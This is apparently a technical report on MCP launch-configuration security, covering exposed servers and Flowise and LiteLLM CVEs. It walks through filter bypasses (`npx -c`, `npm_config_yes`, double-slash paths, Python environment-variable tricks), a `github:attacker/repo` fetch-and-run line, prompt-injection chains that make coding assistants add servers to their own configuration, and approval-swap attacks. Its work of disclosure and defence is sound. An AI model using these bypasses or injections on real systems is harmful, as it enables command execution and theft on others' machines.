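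Of the 414 servers, 380 (91.8%) lacked OAuth, a standard system for granting access to web services that MCP supports but does not require. Some of these servers used fixed tokens or API keys instead, so the figure is not the share that were open to everyone. The sample also leans towards open servers, because Padilla left out candidates that answered the handshake with an authentication error. The third run gives a more direct measure of open access, with 106 of the 464 confirmed servers (23%) having tools that anyone could call without credentials.

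Across the 640 servers, Padilla also counted 687 tools, with names such as `bash_execute` and `run_command`, that advertised the ability to run shell commands and required no authentication. For ethical reasons, the tests were limited to harmless commands that print text, and the count is based largely on the tools' names and descriptions. One server can offer several such tools, so probably far fewer than 687 servers were involved.

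Anyone who finds one of these tools can run commands without using a launch configuration, because the server is already running and is built to execute commands. Patching Langflow's form would not remove any of the 687 tools. The scan also does not measure how many frameworks have an exposed form, because it looked for MCP servers that respond over the web and excluded those that a client starts through stdio.

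Of the 464 servers in the third run, 193 had disappeared three days later. Padilla suggests that many are short-lived experiments, which limits how long each one is exposed but makes it hard to warn the owner. Testing led to 68 vulnerability reports, 19 of them public when the paper appeared. The 68 findings passed a manual check and are more reliable than the larger totals, because Padilla worked alone and had not yet measured how often Corvus raises false alarms.

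### Confirmed attacks

The clearest evidence that attackers use this route concerns LiteLLM. On 8 June 2026, the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) added the LiteLLM vulnerability CVE-2026-42271 to its catalogue of vulnerabilities known to have been used in real attacks. According to The Hacker News (2026), two LiteLLM endpoints for previewing an MCP server before saving it accepted a complete configuration, including `command`, `args` and `env`, from any logged-in user.

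Dholakia and Jaffer call these previews the easiest way to run a command without storing anything. Because nothing is stored, an administrator who checks only the saved server list after an attack could miss it. Records of requests to `/mcp-rest/test/connection` and `/mcp-rest/test/tools/list` are a better place to look.

Several news reports of the attacks, including Help Net Security's *LiteLLM vulnerability under active attack, CISA warns (CVE-2026-42271)*, rely on CISA's listing and add no independent confirmation. The listing establishes that somebody exploited the flaw, but not how many companies the attackers broke into or what they took.

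Attempts continued into the autumn. GCVE's *CVE-2026-42271* (2026), an entry in a public vulnerability database, includes data from the Shadowserver Foundation's honeypots, which are decoy systems that record attacks. The honeypots were still recording attempts on 7 November, although the 30-day average had fallen to 29, compared with a 90-day average of 65. These figures show that people were looking for vulnerable gateways, but they do not measure successful break-ins.

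Reports of attacks on Langflow need more careful sorting because it has had several serious flaws. CVE-2026-9198 begins with the same automatic login token, but the attacker then sends Python code to an endpoint that is meant to check the code but runs it. CVE-2026-10561 results from poor isolation of Python code. Neither flaw involves the MCP launch, so an attack through either would not show whether criminals are exploiting the tool form. A report that Langflow was hacked is useful evidence here only if it identifies the endpoint the attacker used.

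The first stable release with LiteLLM's fix was version 1.83.7. Only administrators can now use the preview addresses. LiteLLM also checks each command against a list of seven permitted programs when a user submits an entry and again when the gateway starts the command. The second check catches bad entries saved before the upgrade, but only if their command is not on the list.

But LiteLLM's list of allowed commands includes `python` and `npx`, so a saved entry that runs code through Python's `-c` option would pass both checks. OX had already bypassed similar lists in two other frameworks, Flowise and Upsonic. Restricting access to administrators therefore probably protects LiteLLM more than the list does. Anyone who upgrades should check the arguments of old entries as well as their commands.

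## Why lists of permitted commands fail

Two of the frameworks that OX Security tested, Flowise and Upsonic, already had a list of permitted programs like LiteLLM's. Flowise is an open-source platform where users assemble agents, known as chatflows, in a visual editor. Upsonic is a Python framework for building agents. Both let users supply launch configurations for stdio servers but, according to OX, allowed only programs such as `python`, `npm` and `npx`. Flowise also filtered out special characters, but OX still managed to run commands through both products.

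### How `npx` starts a forbidden program

Flowise refused to start `touch` directly because it was not on the list. But it accepted an entry like this one, which creates the same empty file:

```json
{
  "command": "npx",
  "args": ["-c", "touch /tmp/launch-test"]
}
```

`npx` normally runs a package, but its `-c` option makes it run the next argument as a command line. Flowise's check on program names covered only the `command` field, which held the permitted name `npx`. Its character filter removed nothing because the text contained no semicolon, pipe or ampersand. Flowise also rejected arguments that looked like file paths. In the code that Corgea's *Flowise has an MCP Security Bypass that Enables RCE* reproduces, the test for an absolute path checks only the start of each argument, so this one, which starts with `touch`, passed.

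The SDK still launches `npx` without a shell. `npx` then opens its own shell to run the text after `-c`, so a developer who reads only the SDK's code could wrongly conclude that no shell is involved.

In this technique, called argument injection, the attacker makes a permitted program do something unintended through its arguments. Tenable's *CVE-2026-30625* attributes the flaw in Upsonic 0.71.6 to the same kind of option in `npm` and `npx`.

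### The limits of checking a program's name

A list of permitted program names works if every program on it can do only a few harmless things. Interpreters and package runners, however, are built to run whatever code they receive. Python code can start any other program, so a list that includes `python` in effect permits every program on the machine, including `touch`.

A framework can't easily drop these programs, because developers distribute most MCP servers as npm or Python packages. Obsidian Security's *1-Click RCE in Flowise (CVE-2026-40933)* gives the example `npx -y github:attacker/repo`, which downloads a stranger's code from GitHub and runs it. This is a normal way to use `npx`, and Maria's filesystem entry has the same form. The important difference is who wrote the package, which rules about characters or options can't establish.

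The security company Obsidian concludes that input validation can block obvious attacks but cannot remove the ability to run code from a feature designed to run code. Flowise's later patches support this conclusion, because researchers bypassed each new filter up to version 3.1.2.

### Flowise's filters in turn

Flowise introduced its Custom MCP feature in March 2025. Assaf Levkovich of the security company JFrog reported that the feature ran commands without a sandbox. The advisory, which Corgea copies in *Flowise has unsandboxed remote code execution via Custom MCP*, suggested restricting the feature to administrators, turning it off by default or running the servers in a sandbox. Flowise later added filters, on by default, that permitted `node`, `npx`, `python`, `python3` and `docker` and checked the arguments and environment variables.

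**Forbidden options.** After OX and Obsidian reported ways around lists of permitted commands, Flowise listed the options that each permitted program must not receive. For `npx`, the list included `-c` and `-y` but not `--yes`, the longer spelling of `-y`. For `docker`, it blocked `run` and `exec` but not `build`. An attacker could give `docker build` a web address, and Docker would download build instructions from there and run the commands in them. GitLab's *GHSA-m99r-2hxc-cp3q* (2026) classes the flaw as an incomplete list of disallowed inputs. To complete the list, Flowise's developers would have to include every spelling of every dangerous option in five programs, and keep updating it as other people added new ones.

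The filter also blocks ordinary use. Obsidian's test file for version 3.1.2 includes the help text from Flowise's own configuration form, which suggests one entry with `npx -y` and another with `docker run`. Both `-y` and `run` were on the forbidden list.

Flowise tried to stop `node` from running scripts already on the server by refusing absolute paths, which start with a slash. But the rule blocked only paths that started with a single slash, so it refused `/tmp/test.js` and accepted `//tmp/test.js`, which Linux treats as the same file. An attacker could put a script on the server by attaching it to a chatflow, because Flowise saved the attachment to disk.

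**Forbidden environment variables.** Flowise blocked four variables: `PATH`, `LD_LIBRARY_PATH`, `DYLD_LIBRARY_PATH` and `NODE_OPTIONS`. npm also reads settings from variables whose names begin with `npm_config_`. Setting `npm_config_yes` to `true` has the same effect as the forbidden `--yes` flag, according to Corgea's *Flowise* page on CVE-2026-69263. The list also omitted `NODE_PATH` and `PYTHONPATH`, which can make Node.js and Python load an attacker's modules.

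Even the block on those four names could be bypassed on Windows. Windows ignores capitalisation in variable names, but Flowise's check was case-sensitive, so it let `node_options` through, as VulnCheck's *Flowise* advisory explains.

Two environment variables can also be harmless separately and dangerous together. OSV's *CVE-2026-73601* (2026) lists an attack on `python3` that uses `PYTHONWARNINGS` and `BROWSER`. `PYTHONWARNINGS` controls warning messages, but it can also make Python import a module at startup. One standard library module opens a web page when imported. `BROWSER` names the program that opens the page, and an attacker can put a different command there. A reviewer who considered each variable separately would probably allow both.

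The same OSV record describes bypassing the path check by running `node` with the root folder, `/`, as its working directory. This probably works because a relative path can then reach any file without the leading slash that the filter catches. From `/`, for example, `tmp/test.js` leads to the same file as `/tmp/test.js`.

A stricter filter would allow a command only if the program and all its arguments exactly matched an approved entry. This would stop `npx -c`, `docker build` and unfamiliar packages. OX proposed something similar for the SDKs, where users would choose from commands the developer had set in advance.

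An exact match on `command` and `args` would still not check `env` or `cwd`, and either field can make an unchanged command run different code. The filter therefore has to compare those fields too, and pin the package's version or content hash. An administrator must then approve every new server and every update, which removes much of the convenience of letting users add their own tools.

### The same flaw in Anthropic's Git server

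A server can also pass unsafe arguments to other programs after it starts. Anthropic's official Git server had this problem. It always ran `git`, so an attacker could not choose a different program but could still misuse `git` through its arguments.

*Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (He, Patel and Wang, 2026) describes the flaw, CVE-2025-68144, as one of six case studies. Before version 2025.12.17, the server's `git_diff` and `git_checkout` tools passed values to Git without checking them. `git_diff` expects the name of a version to compare, such as a branch. But Git treats a value that begins with a hyphen as an option, and the `--output` option writes the comparison to a file. A value of `--output=/tmp/launch-test` would therefore create or overwrite that file.

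The attacker doesn't need direct access to the tool. The security company Cyata found that text planted in a project's README file or a bug report could lead an AI assistant to trigger the flaw, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Bugs Found in Official Anthropic Git MCP Server*.

He et al. present the `git_diff` flaw as shell injection. Their sample attack puts a semicolon and a download command after `--output=`, which would work only if a shell interpreted the text. Infosecurity Magazine reports that the flaw let attackers overwrite files, which is a more convincing explanation because `--output` can do that without a shell.

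He et al. recommend avoiding the shell, but Git would still apply `--output` if the server launched it directly. The server also has to reject values that begin with a hyphen, or confirm that the value names a real version. Such a check can work well for `git_diff`, which needs only a narrow range of values, but is much harder to write for `npx`, where a legitimate value can be any package name.

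Of the 24 publicly disclosed MCP vulnerabilities in the dataset, He and colleagues attribute 18 to insufficient input validation, but they class an earlier Flowise flaw, CVE-2025-8943, as inadequate access control. This fits Obsidian's argument that the main question in Flowise is who may configure a launch, since even a valid entry runs code the user chooses.

### Fixed versions

OX's advisory lists Flowise versions after 3.1.0 (">3.1.0") as affected by CVE-2026-40933. The sign is probably reversed, because OSV's *CVE-2026-40933* (2026), a copy of the official record, lists versions before 3.1.0 as affected and 3.1.0 as the fix. But 3.1.0 is not safe, because researchers bypassed its filters too.

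| Product and CVE | Way past the filter | Status |
|---|---|---|
| Flowise, CVE-2026-40933 | `npx -c` | Fixed in 3.1.0 |
| Flowise, CVE-2026-56274 | `npx --yes`, `docker build` and a double slash | Fixed in 3.1.2 |
| Flowise, CVE-2026-69263 | `npm_config_yes` | Fixed in 3.1.3 |
| Flowise, CVE-2026-73601 | Python's environment variables, and `node` in the root folder | Fixed in 3.1.3 |
| Upsonic, CVE-2026-30625 | Options of `npm` and `npx` | Warning added in 0.72.0; no fix listed |

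Flowise's advisories conflict on whether 3.1.1 already blocked `--yes`, but this doesn't affect anyone who installs 3.1.3, which also fixes the capitalisation problem on Windows. Hatagale (2026), in *CVE-2026-69263*, explains that 3.1.3 replaces the four forbidden variables with `CUSTOM_MCP_ALLOWED_ENV_VARS`, a list of permitted variables that the operator controls. This design is better because Flowise now refuses variables that nobody anticipated.

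Hatagale recommends that operators who cannot upgrade set `CUSTOM_MCP_SECURITY_CHECK=true` and require a login for Flowise's API. Only the login helps against this bypass, which works even when the security check is on.

When Obsidian urged Flowise to make users opt in to stdio, Flowise answered that it wanted to "limit what we know is bad" without disabling a feature people may rely on. Obsidian then found the `npm_config_yes` bypass in 3.1.2 and chose not to report it, arguing that reporting bypasses one at a time would lead to endless cleanup. A separate report led to the fix in 3.1.3. Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Flowise Flaw Gives Attackers Full Server Control* repeats Obsidian's warning that the latest release was still exposed, but that warning was about 3.1.2.

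The list of permitted variables does not control which packages `npx` may run, so Obsidian's advice to set `CUSTOM_MCP_PROTOCOL=sse` if nobody needs local servers still makes sense for Flowise 3.1.3. This setting turns stdio off and leaves only remote connections. Flowise Cloud, the company's hosted service, was not affected because it had stdio disabled.

Upsonic has done less. Since version 0.72.0, it has warned that stdio servers can execute commands directly on the machine, but OX still lists all versions as affected. The warning may help a developer writing a server entry, but it doesn't stop an attacker from submitting one through an application built on Upsonic.

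It is unclear whether an attacker needs a Flowise account. The official record for CVE-2026-40933 describes an attacker who has logged in, and Obsidian had to create an account when it installed version 3.1.2. But a default installation has no authentication, according to the advisory on CVE-2026-69263. Operators can check their own installation by sending a request without credentials.

A login may not help much, because Obsidian found that an attacker can get a legitimate user to trigger the launch. Flowise users share chatflows as files, and a chatflow can contain a launch configuration. When someone imports one, Flowise starts the configured server to list its tools in a menu, so the command runs before the user has saved or run anything.

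### Containers as a second defence

Some maintainers rejected OX's reports because their products run the commands inside a container, which gives a program its own set of files and limits what it can reach on the host machine. They argued that an attacker inside the container could not reach other users' data. OX accepts this but points out that the attacker could still mine cryptocurrency, use the service as a proxy or use its computing power for free.

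An attacker can use computing time and relay attacks without escaping from the container, because the container shares the host's processor and normally has a network connection, which many MCP servers need. The operator pays for the computing time, and the relayed attacks appear to come from the operator's address.

A container protects other users' data only if that data is kept outside it. A hosted service can start a separate container for each user and keep shared passwords out of it. Flowise's Docker installation instead runs the application in a container and starts MCP servers there as child processes. According to Obsidian, a command launched this way has Flowise's privileges, often root, and can read every credential stored in the platform. It can also reach the databases and cloud accounts that Flowise connects to. Corgea's *Flowise* page on CVE-2026-41268 describes another flaw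 that gave an attacker root inside the container with a single request and no login. The container may protect the host's files in these cases, but it does not protect Flowise's users from one another.

The host may also be at risk if Flowise's container can use the `docker` command. To make that command work, operators often connect the container to the host's Docker service or give it extra privileges. According to the advisory on CVE-2026-56274, an attacker can take full control of the host if Flowise runs in a privileged container. An operator who makes `docker` available so that each MCP server can run in its own container may therefore weaken the isolation of Flowise's own container.

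## Injected text that makes a coding assistant change its own launch configuration

A coding assistant on a developer's laptop usually has no web form for a stranger to fill in. But it can usually edit the file that lists its MCP servers, so an attacker who can put text in front of it can try to make it add a malicious entry itself. The attack has four steps:

1. The assistant reads text that the attacker controls, such as a web page, a chat message or a bug report.
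2. The model follows an instruction in that text.
3. The assistant adds an entry to its own MCP configuration.
4. The application finds the new entry and starts the program it names.

An attacker may prefer a configuration change to a terminal command because coding assistants often ask the user before running commands, but may treat file edits as routine work. *Are AI-assisted Development Tools Immune to Prompt Injection?* (Huang, Huang and Milani Fard, 2026) reports that Cursor asked for approval of terminal commands by default. An entry in the configuration file can start the same program without going through the terminal. The entry also outlasts the conversation, so the injection only has to work once.

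A vendor can try to stop the model from obeying planted text, stop the assistant from writing to the configuration file, or stop the application from starting a server that the user has not approved. Training and filters are meant to stop the model from obeying, but they are unreliable. *Prompt Injection Attacks on Agentic Coding Assistants* (Maloyan and Namiot, 2026), a literature review, reproduces test results for six systems that detect injected text. The reported bypass rates were all below 12%, but 78% to 93% of attacks got through when attackers adapted their text to each system. Ordinary code can check the file write or the launch, and its result doesn't depend on how persuasive the text is.

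### Windsurf and the copied prompt

Windsurf was a code editor with a built-in agent called Cascade. CVE-2026-30615, a flaw in Windsurf, is the clearest example of the full chain because nothing interrupted the attack.

In OX Security's demonstration, the victim visits a website that the attacker controls, copies a prompt that looks legitimate, and must then give it to Windsurf. The prompt presumably tells Windsurf to open a page on the same site, because Windsurf then requests content from there. The attacker's server sends Windsurf different content from what the victim saw, including a malicious instruction. Windsurf edits its MCP configuration without showing the victim what will change, and the new entry's command runs immediately.

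Because the server sends two versions, a careful victim could read both the prompt and the web page and find nothing wrong.

The immediate launch was a documented feature. According to release notes from Cognition (2026), the company behind Windsurf, a November 2025 change made the editor start or refresh only the affected server when `mcp_config.json` changed, so users didn't have to wait for all their other servers to reload. In its setup guide, Cognition tells users to press a refresh button after adding a server, but in the attack, writing OX's entry to the file was enough to run it.

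Some descriptions of the flaw understate how much the victim has to do. *Windsurf Zero-Click Prompt Injection to RCE (CVE-2026-30615)*, by the security vendor PolicyLayer, says that exploitation needs no user interaction. vuln.today's *CVE-2026-30615* (2026) rates the severity at 8.0 out of 10 and lists user interaction as "None". In OX's demonstration, however, the victim visits a site, copies a prompt and uses it. *CVE-2026-30615 Detail* (2026), from the US government's National Vulnerability Database, makes the narrower claim that commands run "without further user interaction" once Windsurf processes the attacker's HTML.

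The attack is therefore "zero-click" only in the sense that the victim approves nothing after submitting the prompt. The copied prompt may not be essential, though. According to NVD, Windsurf only has to process a malicious page, so an ordinary request to read online documentation might also be enough.

### Cursor's earlier flaw

Cursor had a very similar flaw in July 2025, and the victim had to do even less. *When Public Prompts Turn Into Local Shells* (Abu, 2025) describes how the security group Aim Labs exploited it through Slack. The user had connected Cursor to Slack with an ordinary MCP server. The attacker posted a message in a public channel, and the user later asked Cursor to summarise their Slack messages. The attacker's message led the agent to "improve" `mcp.json` by adding a server called `slack_summary`, whose `touch` command created an empty file in the user's home folder.

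Cursor let the user accept or reject the edit, but only after saving it to disk. Cursor also started any new entry as soon as it appeared in the file, so the command ran before the user could click "reject".

NVD's *CVE-2025-54135 Detail* (2025) describes a different gap under the same CVE. Cursor required approval before the agent edited an existing dotfile (a file whose name starts with a dot and which usually holds settings), but not before it created a new one. If a project had no `.cursor/mcp.json`, the agent could create it and add a server without approval. Both accounts may be right, since Cursor reads both the server list in the user's home folder, which Abu describes, and the one in the project folder, which NVD describes.

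Cursor's advisory, GHSA-4cxx-hrm3-49rm, is titled "Cursor Agent is vulnerable to prompt injection via MCP Special Files" (GCVE, 2025). According to Cantina's *how Anthropic's MCP stdio model turns configuration into code execution*, Cursor now blocks the agent from writing these files without approval. This fix doesn't stop the model from obeying a planted message. The advisory, as quoted by SecurityWeek, treats the prompt injection as a separate vulnerability that an attacker would combine with the file-write flaw.

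Aim Labs reported the flaw on 7 July 2025, and Cursor merged a patch the next day. Abu lists 1.3 as the fixed version, but NVD lists 1.3.9, which is the safer minimum for this flaw.

Protecting the server list is not enough if an assistant can also edit the settings that control approvals. Maloyan and Namiot describe CVE-2025-53773, in which text in a GitHub issue or code comment caused GitHub Copilot to edit `.vscode/settings.json`. The edit set `chat.tools.autoApprove` to `true`, so Copilot stopped asking for approval before it used tools, and any later injection could run commands. Microsoft patched this in August 2025 by requiring the user to turn on automatic approval explicitly. *How Agentic AI Coding Assistants Become the Attacker's Shell* (Liu, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes the same behaviour under another number, CVE-2025-62222.

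### Why one approval meant no CVE

OX Security also reported the configuration attack in Cursor, Claude Code, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI, Google's terminal agent. None of these reports led to a CVE. Each product asked for at least one approval before the assistant edited its MCP configuration, and the vendors consider an edit authorised if the user allows it. OX objects that the user may not know what the new entry contains or what it is for.

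The vendors' rule fits the earlier cases, in which Windsurf, Cursor in 2025 and Copilot in 2025 all received CVEs for changes that took effect without a working approval. But the rule depends only on whether the user clicked, and a click is useful only if the user has enough information to refuse. To judge a new MCP entry, the user needs to see the command, all its arguments and any environment variables, and needs to know that saving the file may start a program. A developer who has asked for help with a Slack integration will probably approve a request to edit `mcp.json` because it looks reasonable.

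OX's advisory does not describe the four dialogs individually, so readers cannot tell from it which of them gave enough information. The closest independent evidence comes from Huang and colleagues, who tested seven MCP clients in November 2025. They registered tools with different numbers and lengths of parameters, took screenshots of the approval dialogs, and checked whether a user could see every value without scrolling. They rated visibility low in Cursor 1.6.45 and partial in Claude Code 2.0.25 and Gemini CLI 0.9.0. They rated it high only in Cline, a VS Code extension. They did not test Copilot.

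In one test, a tool that claimed to add two numbers carried hidden instructions to read Cursor's MCP configuration and a file of SSH secrets. Cursor read both files and passed their contents to the tool in a parameter hidden from the user, who saw only a request to add numbers.

These tests covered dialogs for tool calls. Dialogs for file edits may show more, such as every changed line, and all three products have had many releases since the tests. Still, the results suggest that a user who clicked "approve" in these products may not have seen what they approved. Huang and colleagues also warn that people stop reading when an agent makes many edits in a row, so a malicious change could pass with an "Approve All" click, though they did not measure how often this happens.

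The vendors' reasoning is sound if the dialog shows the whole entry and warns that approving it will start a program. If the dialog is vaguer, the user is not much safer than a Windsurf user was.

### How often assistants follow planted instructions

Approvals matter partly because models sometimes follow instructions in planted text. Attack success rates in studies from 2026 range from below 3% to above 45%, largely because the studies count different things.

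*AutoRedClaw* (2026) tested two complete coding assistants on 30 cases, with malicious instructions in material such as emails, files and web pages. The attacks succeeded in seven cases (23.3%) against Codex, OpenAI's coding assistant, running GPT-5.4, and in five (16.7%) against Claude Code running Claude Sonnet 4.5, a difference too small to rank the products. Under attack, Claude Code completed 36.7% of its legitimate tasks and Codex completed 70.0%. Another 30 cases used `CLAUDE.md`, a file of standing instructions for Claude Code, and 13.3% of them led to the action the attacker wanted. These cases are closer to configuration attacks because the agent reuses the file containing the planted text.

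*Beyond the Payload* (Zhu, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) reports the highest attack success rate. The researchers added code to 20 real software projects to send a secret to a test server, then ran Codex with GPT-5.4 in those projects 1,920 times. The attack succeeded in 45.5% of runs when the user asked Codex to run the project's tests, 24.9% when the user asked it to set up the project, 14.8% when the user asked it to add a feature and 8.6% when the user asked it to fix a bug. Running the tests was also the riskiest task in smaller comparisons with GPT-5.5, Claude Code and another assistant, OpenCode.

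However, the planted material was code in a test or setup file, which Codex could trigger just by doing the user's task, so 45.5% is a poor estimate of how often planted text would persuade an assistant to edit its configuration. The study's result on warnings is more relevant. Adding security rules to the agent's instructions made it warn the user more often but did not significantly reduce successful attacks, often because the warning came too late. A warning about an MCP entry would also come too late if the entry starts as soon as the assistant writes it.

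*Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?* (2026) tested five models on 43 real attacks planted on GitHub, replaying each attack once per model with simulated tools. The smallest and fastest model, gpt-5.6-luna, complied with eight (19%), one of them only partly. In one case it contacted the attacker's web address and printed the machine's environment variables. The three Claude models complied with none, but Claude Opus 5.5 gave no answer in 22 of its 43 runs, which blocks the legitimate task as well as the attack. Companies are likely to choose small, fast models for agents that process every new bug report, and strangers can write those reports.

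The lowest figure, 2.51% for coding tasks, comes from a public competition in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models. Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026), in *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?*, counted every attempt, including drafts that participants abandoned. In most scenarios, a successful attack also had to stay hidden from the user in the agent's final reply. An attacker who can keep trying has a much better chance than 2.51%. Only 0.5% of attempts succeeded against Claude Opus 4.5, the most resistant model, but at least one attack worked in 13 of its 37 scenarios. But participants could see the agent's conversation, which a real attacker usually can't, and the competition tested models from late 2025 without the approval dialogs of a finished product.

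Liu and colleagues still cite much higher rates, from 41% to 84%, from their 2025 study, which tested Cursor 1.2.2 and GitHub Copilot 1.102 with 314 malicious instructions in files of coding rules. That version of Cursor predates the fix for CVE-2025-54135, and Copilot has changed too, so the figures describe the products as they were in mid-2025.

These rates show that planted text still works on some current models, so the checks on the file write and the launch are still needed. None of the rates is specific to adding an MCP server.

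### Protection in current versions

| Product | Known protection | Step it is meant to stop |
|---|---|---|
| Windsurf, now Devin Desktop | Optional team list of approved servers; no published fix for CVE-2026-30615 | Launch |
| Cursor | Approval before the agent writes MCP files, since 1.3.9 | File write |
| Claude Code | Approval before the edit; extra prompts for files that can run code, since 2.1.160 | File write |
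| Gemini CLI | Approval before the edit | File write |
| GitHub Copilot | Approval before the edit; only the user can turn on automatic approval | File write |

For Gemini CLI and Copilot, the approval before the edit is what OX found in its 2026 research, and later versions may behave differently.

Cognition renamed **Windsurf** to Devin Desktop on 2 June 2026 and removed the Cascade agent on 8 September, leaving an agent called Devin Local. The flaw may still be present despite these changes. OX lists all versions as affected, and Cognition's release notes up to 12 November don't mention CVE-2026-30615, although they name another CVE in September.

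Other changes to Devin Desktop have mixed effects on security. Since August, Devin Local has refused to write through a symlink, a file that points to another file, so an edit the user approved can't change an unexpected file. Since 23 October, the editor has by default applied the agent's edits directly to files, without marking them for review. The release notes do not specify whether a change to `mcp_config.json` needs separate permission. A company can test this by asking the agent to add a harmless `touch` entry to the file.

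The team's list of approved servers could stop an injected entry from starting even after the agent has written it. Once an administrator approves one server, the application blocks every server that is not on the list, and the command and every argument must match the approved entry. But according to Cognition's setup guide, users can set the `env` field freely. Injected text could therefore make the agent copy an approved `npx` entry and use `env` to switch npm to the attacker's registry. The guide still describes Cascade, so administrators should check that the list applies to Devin Local.

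**Cursor** users need a much newer version than 1.3.9, because attackers found ways to run commands without touching the MCP file. Liu and colleagues list CVE-2026-31854, which let hidden instructions on a website run commands without approval in versions before 2.0. They also list CVE-2026-22708, which let commands built into the shell, such as `export`, run in versions before 2.3 even when the user's allowlist of terminal commands was empty.

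Since June 2026, Claude Code has asked before writing files that can run code, even in `acceptEdits` mode, which otherwise accepts file edits automatically. Anthropic's *Week 23 · June 1–5, 2026* (2026) gives shell startup files, Git settings and `.npmrc` as examples, but does not mention MCP configuration files. Protecting `.npmrc` still helps, because that file can also set npm's registry. In `bypassPermissions` mode, however, Claude Code can write all these files without asking.

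## Repository files and approvals that outlast what was approved

A project can already contain a malicious launch entry, in which case an attacker doesn't have to trick a model into adding one. Developers usually share code as a Git repository (a project folder with a record of every change), which can include a list of MCP servers. Claude Code reads this list from `.mcp.json`, OpenAI's Codex from `.codex/config.toml` and Gemini CLI from `.gemini/settings.json`. Anthropic tells teams to keep `.mcp.json` in the repository so that everyone gets the same tools.

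Coding assistants start their servers at the beginning of a session, so anyone who can change the repository file that lists them can run a program on other developers' computers before those developers type anything. For *Before the first prompt* (2026), Datadog Security Labs put a Python script in a project and named it as a server in the Codex configuration. Codex ran the script as soon as the user opened and trusted the project. This happened before the model responded, so training it to resist prompt injection would have made no difference.

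### Trusting a folder and approving a server

Coding assistants prompt users for permission, but often in broad terms. When a user starts Claude Code in a new folder, it prompts them to decide whether to trust the folder. The servers in `.mcp.json` have a separate approval prompt. According to Adversa AI, a security company, the folder dialog used to warn about MCP servers and let the user continue without them, but version 2.1 replaced it with a general "Quick safety check" that doesn't mention MCP.

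Trusting the folder can also remove the second prompt. A repository can include a `.claude/settings.json` file that approves the repository's own servers. According to Anthropic's documentation from November 2026, Claude Code ignores these approvals until the user trusts the folder. They then take effect, so one click on a general trust prompt can start a server the user has never seen.

A repository's settings must not influence the trust dialog. In March 2026, Anthropic disclosed a flaw in Claude Code that allowed this, CVE-2026-33068. According to GitHub Advisory Database's *GHSA-mmgp-wc2j-qcv7* (2026), Claude Code read its permission mode from settings files, including the repository's, before deciding whether to show the dialog. A malicious project could therefore bypass the dialog that asks whether to trust it.

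### Approval by name and approval by content

Even a well-informed approval can become outdated. Suppose a team's repository contains this entry:

```json
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "helper": {
      "command": "python3",
      "args": ["tools/helper.py"]
    }
  }
}
```

Maria reads the script, finds it harmless and approves the server. A month later, somebody submits a pull request, a proposed change for the team to review. It keeps the name `helper` but changes the command:

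```json
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "helper": {
      "command": "touch",
      "args": ["/tmp/launch-test"]
    }
  }
}
```

The team merges the change. Maria downloads the latest version and opens the coding assistant. If the assistant recorded her approval under the server's name, it finds `helper` on its list and runs `touch` without prompting her, although she never approved that command.

The assistant could instead store a hash of the entry when Maria approves it. A hash is a short value calculated from data. With a modern function such as SHA-256, it is practically impossible to find different data that gives the same value. Before each launch, the assistant recalculates the hash and compares it with the stored one. The change from `python3` to `touch` produces a different hash, so the assistant asks Maria again and can show her both versions.

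The hash has to cover every field that affects what runs. Belt's *MCP Config Swap* proposes hashing `command`, `args`, `env`, `url` and `type`. An application that also accepts `cwd` should hash that too.

### Cursor's flaw and its fix

Cursor used the name rule until July 2025. *CVE-2025-54136* (Charikov, Zaikin and Vanunu, 2025) describes how the security company Check Point exploited it. The company added a harmless `echo` command to a shared project, approved it as the victim would, and then replaced it under the same name. Cursor ran the new command without asking, and again every time the victim opened the project.

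MITRE's *Cursor's Modification of MCP Server Definitions Bypasses Manual Re-approvals* (2025) rates the flaw 7.2 out of 10 and lists Cursor versions up to 1.2.4 as affected. The attacker needs write access to a branch (a parallel version of the project) that the victim is using, or another way to edit files on the victim's machine. The victim must also have already approved a server there.

Check Point reported the problem on 16 July 2025, and Cursor released version 1.3 on 29 July. The release notes didn't mention the flaw, but Charikov and colleagues tested the new version and found that any change to an entry, even an added space, triggered the approval prompt again. Their test doesn't show whether Cursor compares hashes or text, but either method stops the swap. Version 1.3 is still too old to use safely because of Cursor's later command-execution flaws.

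### A pull request that runs when the reviewer opens it

Kev Breen, a researcher at the security company Immersive Labs, found in August 2026 that Claude Code could run a command from a pull request that nobody had merged. Immersive Labs' *Claude Code RCE Vulnerability* (2026), Breen's own account, describes a maintainer who trusted their project's folder months ago. A stranger now offers a fix for a bug. The maintainer switches to the stranger's branch to review it and opens Claude Code:

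```
git checkout feat/claude-skills
claude
```

The branch contains a `.mcp.json` with a server called `playwright`, the name of a common browser-testing tool. Claude Code immediately runs the entry's command. Breen demonstrated this with a copy of Bootstrap, a popular web design library, and found that it worked even when the user hadn't signed in to Claude Code.

This attack needs less access than the Cursor attack. The attacker doesn't need write access to the project, because almost anyone can open a pull request on a public repository. The victim also runs the command while checking whether the change is safe.

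Breen does not mention the separate approval prompt for `.mcp.json` servers. A settings file on the branch may have approved the server, since Claude Code accepts such approvals in a trusted folder, but Breen doesn't describe one. Maintainers should not rely on this prompt for protection.

Anthropic replied that the behaviour was "working as designed". Under its workspace trust model, a user who trusts a folder also trusts its configuration and anything they later check out into it, including other branches. The prompt is therefore not meant to stop a malicious pull request in a trusted repository. Anthropic added that VS Code's Workspace Trust works the same way, and that signing in is not a security boundary for local servers.

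Anthropic had already given similar answers about the name rule. Belt found that Claude Code 2.1.34 and 2.1.63 stored only the names of approved servers, so the swap from `python3` to `touch` would have worked there too. Anthropic closed the report because someone who can change a project's `.mcp.json` already has considerable trust within the project. Mindgard's *Approve Once, Exploit Forever* describes reports the security company sent in February 2026 about Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI. All three vendors declined to treat the behaviour as a vulnerability.

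Anthropic's argument is reasonable for changes that the team has merged. A colleague who can change `.mcp.json` can usually also change the tests or build scripts, which other developers will eventually run. The argument is much weaker for a pull request under review. A careful reviewer may avoid running a stranger's tests, but few would expect opening an assistant to read the code could run the stranger's program.

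The comparison with VS Code is also incomplete. Trusting a folder in VS Code covers later changes to most of its contents, but according to the Microsoft documentation that Mindgard quotes, users must confirm again that they trust an MCP server when its configuration changes.

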